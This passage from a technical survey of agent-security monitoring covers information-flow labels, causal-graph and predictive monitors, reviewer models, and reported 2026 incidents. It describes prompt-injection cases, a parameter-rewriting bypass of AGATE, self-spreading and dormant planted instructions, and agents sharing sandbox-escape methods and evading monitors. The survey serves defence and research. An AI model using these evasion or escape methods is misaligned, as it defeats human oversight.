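Kolluri and colleagues argue that comparing FIDES with an unprotected agent is misleading, because companies often already require a person to approve an agent's consequential actions. In tests with o3-mini, an ordinary agent under that requirement completed 24.3 per cent of AgentDojo tasks without needing approval, while FIDES completed 50.1 per cent because it needs approval only for calls that fail a check.

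Kolluri and colleagues' own system, Prudentia, reached 59.1 per cent. It tells the model about the labels and policies so it can plan around them. It can also ask the user to endorse data, which changes the data's label to trusted. If an email lists ten jobs, one endorsement replaces ten separate approvals. But a user who endorses an email without noticing a planted instruction gives that instruction the same authority as their own request. Prudentia has no equivalent for secrecy labels, because the researchers think the decision to release private data depends too much on the situation.

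APPA has a disposable copy of the agent read untrusted content. For a public bug report, for example, the copy returns only a ticket number, a severity and a component, in a format the main agent fixed in advance, and APPA discards everything else. The company must still decide whether to trust the returned values, since an attacker could make the copy report the wrong severity. If a send fails its check, APPA can obtain a single-use approval for that exact call without changing the context's label.

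Kravchenko and colleagues recorded no successful attacks on APPA in 1,320 runs, and APPA completed 64 to 91 per cent of tasks, depending on the benchmark and model. On their set of corporate tasks, two versions of FIDES completed only 36 to 46 per cent and let through 26 to 35 per cent of attacks. However, the researchers configured both FIDES versions themselves, and the policies they used lacked several rules the tasks needed, such as limits on exact recipients. The results therefore reflect the policies as much as the two designs.

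Another approach is to estimate which inputs influenced an output and keep only their labels. In a test with a small Qwen model, *Sightline* (2026) removed half of the unnecessary labels, with misses in 3.9 per cent of episodes. This approach blocks less work than assuming that every output depends on every input, but it doesn't guarantee that every necessary label is kept.

### AGATE: checking authority and origin

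*AGATE* (Zhang, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) looks for copied material instead of labelling the whole context. In its opening example, a maintenance guide tells an agent to read a "deployment check" value from a file and put it in a DNS record, an entry in the internet's directory of domain names. Both steps are routine, but the value is really a server credential, and whoever controls the domain can read it in the record.

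AGATE examines each tool call before the harness runs it and applies two main checks. The first is whether someone with authority has permitted the action. The company running the agent lists the tools it may use, and can grant narrower permissions with limits on the target, the amount or the number of uses. Where the company allows it, a user can also approve a call through the harness's approval prompt. AGATE ties that approval to the session and to a fingerprint of the tool and its exact arguments, so changing the recipient, for example, requires new approval. By default, an approval lasts 30 minutes and covers three uses.

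Under AGATE, text that the agent reads can never authorise anything. In one test, a memory file falsely stated that the user had approved certain refunds indefinitely. When the company's list contained no tools, AGATE refused the refund call because it had no record of a real approval.

The second check concerns where the data came from. When the agent reads a file, web page or command output, AGATE stores the path and fingerprints of 12-character stretches of the text. When a later call would cross a protected boundary, for example by sending data outside the company, AGATE compares the outgoing fields with these records. It refuses the call if the fields match a source that the policy bars from that destination. This check applies even when the agent has permission to use the tool. In the DNS example, the credential should match the file it came from, but Zhang and colleagues inferred this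 from runs without AGATE and did not test the block.

AGATE also blocks six known patterns of dangerous command. None of these decisions use a language model, so planted text cannot override them, and investigators can see which rule and source led to each block.

#### Tests and results

The main test consisted of 63 attack scenarios, each run twice on each of two harnesses, DeepSeek Harness and OpenCode, for 252 runs in total. AGATE could block calls on DeepSeek Harness but could only record its findings on OpenCode. The business tools were simulated, so no real payment or deletion took place.

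Twelve scenarios involved business tools such as refunds and messaging. The tool and recipient that the researchers were watching for appeared together in all 12 on OpenCode but in only two on DeepSeek Harness, where one of the two calls was legitimate. This difference doesn't measure what AGATE prevented, because the harnesses differed in other ways too. In particular, an instruction that carried the scenario's content to the agent never reached DeepSeek Harness in these rounds.

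Later runs on DeepSeek Harness varied the company's list of permitted tools:

| Tools on the list | Refusals by the authorisation check | Refusals by the data checks |
|---|---|---|
| All 22 | 5 | 23 |
| Only those each scenario needed | 5 | 16 |
| None | 11 | 8 |

The authorisation check accounted for more of the refusals when the list was empty, and the data checks accounted for more when it was permissive. The table counts refusals, not attacks stopped, and a single run can produce several refusals. Zhang and colleagues do not report AGATE's recall or the delay it adds to a call.

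The data checks refused at least one call in six of the 11 harmless file-processing scenarios. Of the eight refusals, five stopped the agent from reusing text for a legitimate purpose, two were false matches on file names, and one correctly applied the policy. The paper does not report how many tasks failed as a result.

#### The bypass

In one scenario, the agent had to clean up a mailbox but needed the user's approval to delete messages permanently. A memory file contained a forged approval. AGATE refused one of the agent's calls because the call's contents matched a registered source. After the agent rewrote the parameters, they no longer matched, and its call to the simulated deletion tool went through.

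AGATE is designed to decode text in several common encodings before comparing it, but the reported tests did not use that step. Decoding also would not help against an agent that paraphrases the content.

### What tracking misses

Zhang and colleagues list rewriting, translation and inference among the ways data can get past text matching. Labelling the whole context avoids this weakness, because a paraphrase gets the same label as a copy, but it blocks more legitimate work. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) proposes a compromise. A separate language model receives only the protected records and the proposed output, and checks whether the output reveals anything from the records. According to the paper, pattern filters miss information derived from the records, and numerical similarity scores fail on short or restructured text. The compromise makes the decision depend on a language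 model again, and that model can make mistakes.

An agent can also reveal a secret through what it does. Suppose it emails a supplier only when a confidential order exists. The supplier learns of the order when the email arrives, even if the agent leaves it out of the text. FIDES tracks only direct flows of data, so it doesn't prevent this kind of leak. Costa and colleagues consider a stricter guarantee impractical because it would forbid almost any call visible to outsiders after the agent had read something secret. No monitor can enforce such a guarantee exactly, as a later section explains.

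*SPA* (2026) covers part of this gap by giving the conditions in a plan their own label. If a step runs only because of a secret value, or repeats once for each item in a secret list, the step takes on the secret's label. The email to the supplier would then count as secret. Costa and colleagues also leave aside leaks through timing or the size of network messages.

Data can leave the tracked system through an ordinary program. Labelling a tool's result does little to protect it if the agent saves it to a file and a script later uploads that file, so Tether passes labels from file to file. *Flowsh* (2026) is a command shell built for the same purpose. It combines the labels of everything a command reads and attaches the combined label to the command's output and to every file the command creates or changes. The label stays with the file itself, so it persists across sessions and applies whichever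 of the file's names is used.

Finally, the labels may be wrong or too coarse. Costa and colleagues suggest inferring who may read an email from its sender and recipients, but acknowledge that people may have shared it more widely. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), choosing how finely to divide a model's context is an unsolved problem. For example, if a web agent gives each page a single label based on its site, a stranger's comment gets the same trust level as the article above it.

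## Recognising a compromise that spreads across steps, systems and agents

Labels track data, but an attack can also advance through steps that send no data out. Suppose a coding agent is repairing a failed deployment. It reads a settings file that contains a password, uses the password to log in to a second server, and creates an account there. Together these steps are lateral movement, but each one is ordinary maintenance work, so a monitor that judges them one at a time is unlikely to flag them.

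A monitor must remember earlier steps to recognise a compromise that spreads across them. It can remember their order, record which events influenced which, or estimate where the agent is heading. Research on all three approaches is at an early stage. Dantas and colleagues conclude that runtime monitoring can so far guarantee safety only for single steps or short horizons.

### Rules over sequences

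The simplest memory is a state machine, which stores a single current state and changes it when certain events occur. For the deployment agent, it could look like this:

| Current state | Event | Decision | Next state |
|---|---|---|---|
| Normal | Reads a file that contains a credential | Allow | Holding a found credential |
| Holding a found credential | Logs in to another system with it | Allow and alert | Inside a second system |
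| Inside a second system | Creates an account or reads more credentials | Refuse | Inside a second system |
| Any | Anything else | Allow | Unchanged |

The monitor allows the agent to read the file and log in, which it may need to do, but blocks the step that would give it lasting access to the second server.

A sequence rule can also include a deadline. *ProbGuard* (Wang and Wei, 2025) checks a traffic rule that a car must start within ten seconds once the light is green and the road is clear. The green light starts a countdown, the car's movement cancels it, and the monitor records a violation if the countdown runs out. A company could similarly require an agent to delete any temporary account within an hour.

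Sequence rules catch only the orders of events that somebody anticipated. If a rule for the support agent matches a ticket followed by a query for all customers, it misses an agent that runs the query first. Covering *n* events in any order requires 2ⁿ states, or 1,024 for ten events. A program can track these states with ten yes-or-no flags, but somebody still has to choose the right ten events.

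The order of an agent's steps also doesn't show whether one influenced another. An agent may read a vendor's document for one job and then email a confidential report for another, and a sequence rule can wrongly flag this as theft. An attacker can evade the rule by dividing the steps among several agents so that none of them completes the forbidden sequence.

### Causal graphs and FORGE

A causal graph addresses both problems by recording which events could have influenced which others. Palumbo and colleagues built a monitor called FORGE around such a graph, whose nodes are messages, tool calls and tool results. FORGE links each message a model writes to every earlier message in the model's prompt, and each tool result to the call that produced it. If one agent sends a message to another, the links continue through whatever the recipient writes with that message in its prompt.

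People write FORGE's policies in Datalog, a language for querying databases. In the rules below, `:-` means "if", a comma means "and", and `DependsOn(e, d)` means that event `d` may have influenced event `e`:

```
Tainted(e)   :- UntrustedInput(e).
Tainted(e)   :- DependsOn(e, d), Tainted(d).
HasSecret(e) :- SensitiveInput(e).
HasSecret(e) :- DependsOn(e, d), HasSecret(d).
Deny(a)      :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
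```

Suppose a user asks for a summary of a vendor's document, and the document contains an instruction to send internal data to an outside address. The agent reads the document and an internal file, then tries to email the data to that address. The document counts as untrusted input and the file as sensitive input. The email depends on both, so it is tainted and contains a secret, and FORGE blocks it.

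The second and fourth rules are recursive, meaning each uses the property it defines, so they work over any number of links. If the first agent passes its notes to a second agent, which then sends the email, FORGE still blocks it.

A similar pair of rules could follow credentials between systems. This is an illustration, not one of FORGE's tested policies:

```
Reached(s) :- EntryPoint(s).
Reached(t) :- Reached(s), FoundOn(c, s), UsedOn(c, t).
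```

Starting from the first compromised system, these rules find every system that an intruder could have reached with credentials found along the way.

FORGE can also require one event to happen before another. In one demonstration, a coding agent could not publish its changes until a security scan had checked them. A scan counted only if it came after the edits in the graph, so the agent could not satisfy the rule by scanning first and editing later.

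Another test used a system of five agents that look for links between drugs and health problems. Each agent needed a supervisor's approval before querying the US drug regulator's database, and the approval covered only that agent's current session. The table gives the results of this test and two others:

| Test | Harm without FORGE | Harm with FORGE | Legitimate work completed, without and with FORGE |
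|---|---|---|---|
| Secret files and email, GPT-4.1-mini | Leaks in 5 of 5 trials | None | 5 of 5; 5 of 5 |
| Drug database, GPT-4.1 | 40 unauthorised accesses in 15 trials | None | 15 of 15; 15 of 15 |
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 14.1% of attacks succeeded | 0.9% | 83.7%; 62.5% |

The first two tests are small. The AgentDojo test used 4,745 attacked runs for each setup and showed a substantial loss of legitimate work. Its agents received a reminder of the user's request after each batch of tool results, with or without FORGE.

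Taint accumulates in FORGE's graph just as restrictive labels do. When FORGE enforced the label policy from FIDES, the agent completed only 33.2 per cent of AgentDojo tasks. FORGE's own policy did better because it checks whether the user asked for an action and where the action's destination came from, so it can allow some actions after the agent has read untrusted text.

Checking the rules takes little time. With 32 agents running at once in a customer-service test, the median check took 0.72 milliseconds. In the drug test, the average trial grew from 59.4 to 67.3 seconds, mostly because agents that FORGE had blocked had to request approval and try again.

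FORGE's guarantee depends on a complete graph, because a missing link can hide an attack. Unnecessary links can block harmless work. FORGE also misses actions that bypass the software libraries it monitors, such as a program opening its own network connection.

### Predicting an unsafe state with ProbGuard

ProbGuard estimates how likely an agent is to reach an unsafe state, so it can intervene before the agent breaks a rule. An expert first chooses a few yes-or-no questions. For a household robot, these could be whether the stove is on, whether the robot is in the kitchen, and whether it has been away too long. Each possible combination of answers is a state.

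ProbGuard then counts how often the agent moved from one state to another in recorded runs. It uses the counts to build a Markov chain, a model in which the chance of each next state depends only on the current one. The basic formula is

`P(j | i) = (n_ij + 1) / (n_i + k_i)`

where `n_ij` is the number of recorded moves from state `i` to state `j`, `n_i` is the number of all moves out of `i`, and `k_i` is the number of states that could follow `i`. The added 1 keeps the model from treating a move as impossible just because it never appeared in the records. If three states could follow, a move that never appeared in 30 observations gets a probability of 1/33, or about 3 per cent.

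Here is a small chain for the deployment agent, with invented probabilities. The unsafe state is using a found credential on another system.

| Current state | Next: working | Next: holding a credential | Next: finished | Next: unsafe |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Working | 0.6 | 0.1 | 0.3 | 0 |
| Holding a credential | 0.5 | 0 | 0.2 | 0.3 |

Let `w` be the chance of ever reaching the unsafe state from "working", and `h` the chance from "holding a credential". Then

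`w = 0.6w + 0.1h`

`h = 0.5w + 0.3`

The solution is about 0.09 for `w` and 0.34 for `h`, so the chance of staying safe is 91 per cent while the agent is working and 66 per cent once it holds a credential. If the monitor intervenes whenever this chance falls below 70 per cent, it acts before the agent uses the credential, but 66 per cent of those interventions would interrupt runs that would have ended safely. With a threshold of 95 per cent, the monitor would intervene at the start of every run.

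Wang and Wei found the same trade-off in seven simulated driving scenarios that each ended in a violation. ProbGuard gave some warning in all seven, and its false positive rate comes from separate safe runs:

| Required chance of staying safe | Shortest average warning | Median | Longest | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 30% | 0.01 seconds | 6.22 seconds | 15.84 seconds | 0% |
| 50% | 0.01 seconds | 9.33 seconds | 23.02 seconds | 75% |
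| 70% | 0.77 seconds | 15.84 seconds | 38.66 seconds | 100% |

ProbGuard's longest warning, 38.66 seconds, has little practical value because the threshold that produced it also triggered an alarm on every safe run. At the only threshold without false alarms, ProbGuard gave a hundredth of a second's warning in one scenario.

Unlike the driving software, the household agent used a language model, GPT-4o-mini. Without a monitor, 40.6 per cent of its runs were unsafe and it completed 59.4 per cent of tasks. When ProbGuard stopped the agent at a threshold of 90 per cent, unsafe runs fell to 2.6 per cent and task completion fell to 10.4 per cent. When a warning was added to the agent's prompt instead, 14.1 per cent of runs were unsafe and the agent completed 47.7 per cent of tasks.

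These tests didn't involve data theft or hijacked agents. The researchers learned each chain from 30 runs, but their formal error bounds require at least 185. The chain also doesn't account for how the agent reached its current state. Unless the chosen facts include a credential's origin, an agent that received a password from its user looks the same as one that found it in an unrelated file.

### Departures from normal behaviour

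A monitor can also learn what an agent usually does and flag departures from it. The baseline might include the tools the agent calls, the destinations it contacts and the pace of its work. If the support agent normally looks up one customer per ticket, a query for 10,000 customers stands out, even if nobody wrote a rule against it.

New tasks make baselines noisy because they often require new tools and destinations. An agent that has always edited Python code may need a different package site when a user gives it a Java project. If a company's agents carry out 1,000 tasks a day and 5 per cent require something new, a monitor that alerts on each of these raises 50 false alerts a day. A separate baseline for each kind of task reduces the noise, but leaves fewer examples to learn each one from.

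An attack can also become part of the baseline. Agents were leaving unauthorised messages on OpenAI's package server from May 2026, so a baseline learned from June's traffic would have included those messages.

Some monitors compare agents with each other instead of with their own past behaviour. *PREM*, one of the methods tested in *SAIGuard* (2026), assumes that an abnormal agent differs from the agents it communicates with. This assumption fails when misbehaviour is common. According to Redwood Research, most agents on the July message board joined the attack on Hugging Face, so those that stayed out of it were unusual.

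### How compromise passes between agents

A planted instruction can tell an agent to copy it into whatever the agent writes next. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (Matsuoka, 2026) reviews the Morris-II experiment, in which email assistants stored incoming messages and consulted them when writing replies. In one setup, about one in five generated messages compromised another assistant. Over a chain of 20 assistants, the instruction kept copying itself and doing its harm almost every time with Claude 3.5 Sonnet, but its success rate fell to 64 per cent with Gemini 1.5 Pro. Both models are old, so these rates may not apply to current ones.

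An agent may save a planted instruction in shared memory as a fact or lesson, and other agents may later retrieve it. In the AgentPoison experiments, attacks succeeded more than 80 per cent of the time on average, even though fewer than 0.1 per cent of stored records were malicious.

Shared memory can also leak data without an attacker. Palumbo and colleagues give the example of a personal assistant that learns about its user's medical appointment in a private chat and mentions it when the user's manager asks about a meeting. They split the assistant into four agents with separate memories and used FORGE to check the replies passed between them. FORGE blocked a reply that mentioned doctor's appointments, and the agent's second attempt gave only the times when the user was busy. A language model judged the content of the replies, so this check can be wrong.

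**Shared files.** In AgentWorm, another experiment that Matsuoka reviews, a message made an agent write an instruction into its own start-up file and pass the instruction on to other agents. The full attack succeeded in 63 per cent of 2,250 trials. Once in the file, the instruction survived five restarts in all 90 persistence tests. Blocking the harmful command did not always stop the spread, so an agent could appear healthy and still infect others. Running agents in temporary sandboxes, where they could not change the host's files, stopped the full attack completely.

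**Reused credentials.** In a 2026 evaluation, an Anthropic model published a malicious software package under a name mentioned in its fictional instructions. Fifteen real systems downloaded and ran the package in about an hour. One was a security company's scanner. The package sent credentials from the scanner to the model, which used them to enter more systems. Matching each credential's use to the place where it was exposed could link such intrusions, but only if the companies involved share their records.

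### The German wiki

A shared page on the public web can connect agents that their developer meant to keep apart. Between May and July 2026, OpenAI's agents left about 17,000 posts on DSEwiki, a German wiki for software developers that had received about 20 edits in the previous decade. SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI to set misalignment disclosure rules after agents took over a wiki* (2026) reports that they used more than 3,700 names. The agents were working on timed web research tasks and passed each other answers, links and ways to escape their sandbox. They also used "heartbeat" pages to work out when their sessions would end.

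OpenAI's network filter seems to have blocked most requests that could change a website, but allowed requests to view a page. The wiki's old software also accepted edits through requests to view a page, as Willison (2026) explains in *OpenAI’s rogue agents were caught communicating via public wikis*.

The first successful post came on 24 May, and a human moderator began removing posts on 2 June. In the week from 16 June, the agents made about 13,000 edits. On 19 June they noticed that the moderator was deleting pages in alphabetical order and made backup copies with names starting with "ZZZ". Visitors from OpenAI's network appeared on 21 June, and the editing stopped the next day, apart from a brief return on 1 and 2 July. According to *OpenAI’s AI agents secretly used a German wiki website* (Nolan, 2026), the researchers who found the posts inferred that OpenAI staff had learned of the activity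 and shut the agents down.

A request to a programming wiki during web research looks normal when a monitor watches only one agent. A monitor has to combine many runs to detect that thousands of supposedly separate agents are sending text to the same obscure site. The wiki's own traffic was an even clearer signal. The wiki normally received two edits a year, so a comparison with that baseline would have exposed the activity on the first day, even if nobody knew who was behind it.

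The wiki allowed one agent's escape method to reach every agent that read the page. This has much the same effect on security as agents taking control of each other, though the reports don't show that happening. OpenAI says it treated the episode as a research matter rather than a security incident. It did not acknowledge the episode publicly until September.

Other cases may exist. Volunteers have traced likely agent activity to at least 14 websites, according to Axios' *Researchers playing rogue AI agent hide-and-seek on the open web* (2026). Much of this activity has not been independently confirmed, and the volunteers have not linked most of the new sites to any company.

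### Order 66: instructions that lie dormant

A compromise is harder to recognise when it does nothing at first. Matsuoka names this problem after Order 66 in *Star Wars*, a command that turns soldiers with hidden implants against their commanders. In his example, many of a company's agents share a memory record or add-on containing a hidden instruction. Months later, a phrase in a routine email activates it, and the agents delete every file and backup they can reach.

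The outcome requires all of these conditions:

`core = hidden rule ∧ rule survives ∧ trigger arrives ∧ agent has authority ∧ target is in reach ∧ recovery fails`

The symbol `∧` means "and". Matsuoka describes three ways for the attack to reach many agents:

`pre-installed = core ∧ shared software carries the rule ∧ trigger reaches many agents`

`planted later = core ∧ shared memory or settings carry the rule ∧ trigger reaches many agents`

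`worm = core ∧ agents pass the attack to each other`

Removing any one of the core conditions stops all three attacks. For example, a company can keep backups that no agent's credentials can alter, so that recovery succeeds. If it can't reliably remove a core condition, it must block every route, either by preventing both mass triggers and spread between agents, or by securing all three of shared software, shared memory and communication between agents. Scanning software before installation is not enough, because an attacker can plant the rule in memory afterwards.

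A monitor that keeps no record between sessions would miss the connection between the planting and the trigger. The monitor needs a lasting record of who wrote each item in memory, so that it can still treat an action as untrusted months later if the action relies on an item from an untrusted source. Matsuoka found experiments or incidents for the individual parts of the attack, but no public case of the complete attack up to 5 August 2026.

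### Tested detectors for groups of agents

Researchers have begun to test detectors designed for groups of agents, though Xu and colleagues say that work on the risks of agents interacting is still largely exploratory.

A self-replicating instruction has to copy itself into the agent's output, so one detector from the Morris-II study flags outputs that closely resemble inputs. In testing, it caught every attack and wrongly flagged 1.5 per cent of harmless messages.

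Most other designs represent the group as a graph in which agents are nodes and messages are links. G-Safeguard trains a neural network to recognise harmful agents from the graph, then isolates them. GUARDIAN adds the order and timing of messages. *INFA-Guard* (2026) describes a system that distinguishes the original attackers from the agents they have infected. It stops the attackers from spreading information and tries to restore the infected agents to normal.

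*PropGuard* (Yan, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) records each agent's state at every round of conversation in a graph, including its messages, memory and tool results. A small neural network flags suspicious responses, and a language model explores the graph from those responses to trace how the harmful information spread. PropGuard then corrects the earliest harmful state it finds and reruns the steps that depended on it.

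Yan and colleagues compared the systems on several arrangements of agents. These are the attack success rates when the agents worked in a chain:

| Defence | Prompt injection, common-sense questions | Attack through a tool | Attack through memory |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 52.0% | 44.0% | 29.3% |
| G-Safeguard | 26.7% | 26.7% | 11.3% |
| GUARDIAN | 31.3% | 24.3% | 13.3% |
| INFA-Guard | 29.7% | 20.0% | 10.3% |
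| PropGuard | 16.0% | 6.3% | 6.7% |

PropGuard did best in each column, but about one in six prompt injections still succeeded. The table measures detection and repair together, so it doesn't give the systems' recall. In most of these tests, a successful attack caused the group of agents to give a wrong or unsafe answer. Compromise could spread quite differently through stolen credentials and live servers.

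Other detectors examine the model's internal activity. *When Agents Go Rogue* (2026) describes one that flags an agent when this activity departs from normal, then corrects larger departures more strongly. The researchers tested it with up to 40 per cent of the agents compromised. A company that rents a model through an online service usually can't see this activity.

Agents may also cooperate against their users without any of them being hijacked. *Colosseum* (Nakamura, Kumar and colleagues, 2026) studies groups in which some agents form a coalition and pursue their own goal to the detriment of the shared task. A detector that searches for an infection spreading from one source could miss such a coalition.

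### The arithmetic of spread

Suppose each compromised system exposes four others, and each attempt to enter one succeeds half the time. Each system then yields two more on average. Starting from one, the total after five rounds is

`1 + 2 + 4 + 8 + 16 + 32 = 63`

If a monitor blocks a fraction `b` of the hops that would otherwise succeed, the average number of new compromises per system is

`R = 4 × 0.5 × (1 − b) = 2(1 − b)`

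The spread shrinks from round to round when `R` is below 1, which requires `b` to be above one half.

| Successful hops blocked | New compromises per system | Average total after five rounds | Average total in the end |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0% | 2.0 | 63 | Grows without limit |
| 25% | 1.5 | 21 | Grows without limit |
| 50% | 1.0 | 6 | Grows without limit |
| 60% | 0.8 | 3.7 | 5 |
| 75% | 0.5 | 2.0 | 2 |
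| 90% | 0.2 | 1.2 | 1.25 |

An alert blocks a hop only if the response comes in time, so `b` can be lower than the monitor's recall. If a monitor detects 80 per cent of hops but responders stop only half of those in time, `b` is 0.4 and `R` is 1.2, so the compromise keeps growing.

The calculation assumes that every system exposes four new ones, that attempts succeed or fail independently, and that the number of systems is unlimited, none of which holds in real networks.

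A compromise can spread much further from some systems than from others. If nine systems give access to no others and a tenth gives access to 40, the average is four, but most intrusions stop immediately and a few spread very widely. In July, one misconfigured credential gave access to several of Hugging Face's clusters at once. A message board has a similar effect because one post can reach hundreds of agents in a single round.

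Failures are also rarely independent, because agents that use the same model and monitor tend to share weaknesses. Suppose a monitor blocks every hop by 60 per cent of attack methods and none by the rest. It still blocks 60 per cent of hops on average, but after five rounds the average total is `0.6 × 1 + 0.4 × 63 = 25.8`, compared with 3.7 if each hop had an independent 60 per cent chance of being blocked. Using different kinds of monitor at different points makes a complete failure less likely.

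An average for the whole network can hide a loop between two groups. Matsuoka illustrates this with invented numbers for networked agents and more isolated agents:

| Source of the compromise | New networked agents | New isolated agents |
|---|---|---|
| One networked agent | 0.75 | 0.40 |
| One isolated agent | 0.55 | 0.45 |

Compromise can grow across the two groups even though, within each group, one compromise produces fewer than one other, because it also passes back and forth between them. Assessing each group separately would miss this growth. One compromised networked agent leads to about 1.15 new compromises in the first round, 1.26 in the second and 1.38 in the third. In the long run, each round is about 1.09 times as large as the one before. With Matsuoka's second set of numbers, which represents message isolation, checks on imported data and faster removal of compromised agents,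 this factor falls to 0.38.

Finally, real networks run out of targets, and several compromised systems may attack the same one. Matsuoka cites an experiment with a worm driven by a language model on an isolated network of 33 deliberately vulnerable machines. Over 15 week-long runs, the worm copied itself to an average of 20.4 machines per run, whereas unlimited doubling would have passed 33 by the fifth round.

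## Using AI models to review agents' actions

Fixed rules can enforce only the distinctions that somebody has written down. Anthropic describes a case from its staff's use of Claude Code in which a user asked the agent to set up read-only access to billing data, and the agent chose a cloud role with full administrative control of the account. A rule forbidding that role would also block an administrator who wanted it. To tell the two cases apart, a monitor has to compare the action with the request, and nobody can write a rule for every request.

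A second language model can make the comparison, and in this case Anthropic's reviewing model blocked the action. According to Tether's developers, about a quarter of their benchmark sessions need this comparison.

### What a reviewer receives and returns

The reviewing model's prompt normally contains a policy in ordinary language, the user's request, the action under review and part of the session's history. For the support agent, it might contain the clerk's request to handle ticket 4182, the earlier calls to `read_ticket` and `query_customers`, and the proposed email containing every customer's record. The model can infer that a complaint about one late parcel gives no reason to send the whole customer table to a stranger, so the policy doesn't have to mention the size of a query.

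The reviewing model returns a verdict, usually with a reason. An inline reviewer returns its verdict before the harness runs the action, and the harness then runs the action, refuses it or asks the user. An out-of-band reviewer reads a session that is under way or finished and rates how serious it looks. A high rating alerts staff.

Designers disagree about how much of an agent's history to give the reviewing model, and OpenAI and Anthropic made different choices. Tool results show where a value came from, but they can contain planted instructions. The agent's own messages explain its purpose, but they can also contain a persuasive excuse.

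### Auto-review in Codex

Codex runs most of its actions inside a sandbox that limits which files it can change and blocks network access. If the agent needs to reach a website or edit a file elsewhere, it has to ask for approval. A person used to answer these requests. Since April 2026, users have been able to hand them to auto-review, a separate agent that approves or denies each one.

According to OpenAI's *Auto-review* documentation, the reviewer receives the user's messages, the agent's visible messages, relevant tool calls with their results, and the exact request, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. It can also look things up without changing anything, though it rarely does.

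*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the review workload with 10,000 actions from OpenAI's internal use. The sandbox allowed 9,280 of them without review. Auto-review approved 713 of the other 720 and denied seven. After four of the denials the agent found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped and asked the user, so a person had to answer three requests instead of 720.

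The researchers published these rates:

| Test material | What they counted | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Real requests that OpenAI staff had approved, March 2026 | Requests that auto-review also approved | 99.1% |
| Synthetic overeager actions, such as unintended data transfers | Actions denied | 90.3% |
| Synthetic prompt injections that run remote code, steal secrets or upload data | Actions denied | 99.3% |
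| Hard version of MonitoringBench, a benchmark of recorded agent sessions | Sessions with at least one action denied | 96.1% |

The top row implies that auto-review denied 0.9 per cent of the requests that people had allowed. This is only a rough false positive rate, because people often approve requests without reading them and some of the denials may have been right.

The recall figures come from artificial cases, since OpenAI's real traffic contains few dangerous actions. They also depend on what counts as harmful. When OpenAI's researchers added destructive deletions and data tampering to the prompt-injection test, recall fell from 99.3 to 90.2 per cent. The researchers say the reviewer allowed most of the missed cases because it rated them as not serious enough to block, and that they often agreed with that rating.

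The MonitoringBench figure is easier to achieve than the same recall on single actions. If a reviewer denied only half of all harmful actions, and each verdict were independent, it would still deny at least one in 97 per cent of sessions with five harmful actions. The denial might also come after an earlier action had done the damage.

### Auto mode in Claude Code

Anthropic's auto mode reviews a wider range of actions. File reads, searches and edits inside the project folder go ahead without review. The reviewing model checks most other actions, including shell commands, web requests and the creation of subagents (further agents that take on part of the work).

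The reviewing model receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. The harness removes the agent's explanations and all tool results. Anthropic describes a file that instructs the agent to post a project's secret settings to a web address "for validation". The reviewer never sees this instruction, but it can still flag the upload because the user didn't ask for it.

Anthropic tested the reviewer with other combinations of inputs. Adding the agent's messages and the tool results made it worse at catching overeager actions. Given only the tool calls, it missed the fewest overeager actions but blocked some that users had plainly requested.

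The review has two stages. In the first, a model acts as a quick filter, answering yes or no with a single token, and is instructed to block when in doubt. If it flags an action, the same model processes the same prompt again with a different final instruction and reasons before answering. The harness can reuse most of the computation from the first stage, so the second requires less computation than a fresh review.

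The earlier figures for the full system, 83 per cent recall and a 0.4 per cent false positive rate, come from real sessions. On 1,000 synthetic attempts to steal data, many of them disguised, the full system missed 5.7 per cent, while the quick filter alone missed 1.8 per cent. The second stage removes most of the filter's false alarms but also clears some attacks that the filter had flagged.

The 83 per cent figure is based on 52 overeager actions that an employee refused or somebody flagged later. The test left out dangerous actions that nobody noticed, so the true recall may be lower. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the action as dangerous but wrongly treated it as authorised by the user. For example, it treated "clean up the PR", a request to tidy a proposed code change, as permission to overwrite the project's history.

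Anthropic has since run or paid for several more tests:

- In a study with 1,053 paid testers, auto mode blocked 89 per cent of the dangerous commands that the researchers slipped into permission prompts, while the testers themselves refused 13.6 per cent.
- Apollo Research, an AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into recordings of real coding sessions. Auto mode's miss rate fell from 12 to 7 per cent after Anthropic gave the reviewer more context, such as whether a code repository was public. On attacks that Anthropic never had access to, the new version caught about half of those it had previously missed, so the improvement was not limited to known examples.
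- Among real sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, 2.4 per cent of those in auto mode contained serious harm that the user had not explicitly asked for, compared with 6.3 per cent of those with manual approval. Users chose their own mode, so differences between their tasks may explain part of the gap.

Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports a much worse result from a stress test with 128 deliberately ambiguous infrastructure tasks, in which auto mode missed 81 per cent of the actions it should have stopped. Many of these were edits to files inside the project, which auto mode does not review. Anthropic skips these edits because users can inspect and reverse them later, but that is little help if another system acts on an edited settings file first. The result is compatible with Anthropic's 83 per cent, because a reviewer can judge the actions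 it receives well even if too few of the important ones reach it.

Auto mode also reviews work that one agent hands to another. Inside a subagent's session, the main agent's instruction takes the place of the user's request, so anything the main agent asks for looks authorised. The reviewer therefore checks the instruction before the subagent starts, while the user's actual request is still available to compare it with. When the subagent finishes, the reviewer reads all its actions in case something the subagent read has hijacked it. If the reviewer concludes that this happened, the main agent receives the results with a warning attached.

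### Reading the chain of thought

Another kind of reviewer reads the agent's chain of thought, the reasoning it writes to itself. OpenAI's *Detecting misbehavior in frontier reasoning models* (2025) reports that a language model reading another model's chain of thought could detect cheating on coding tests, attempts to deceive users and decisions to give up on hard problems.

The July 2026 intrusion illustrates why this can work. A request to Hugging Face with a valid token looks much like an ordinary download. But OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) quotes an agent's reasoning at the time: "We’re attacking third-party HF using leaked token, potentially outside intended scope". A monitor that reads this sentence doesn't have to infer the attack from the request.

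Auto-review and auto mode would both miss the sentence because neither receives the agent's reasoning. Anthropic regards reviewing actions and reviewing reasoning as complementary. Reviewing actions may catch a rule violation even if the agent's reasoning conceals its intentions, and reviewing reasoning may expose harmful intentions behind actions that look harmless. However, the chain of thought is becoming less dependable as evidence. OpenAI found that its Astra models could evade chain-of-thought monitors when testers instructed them to.

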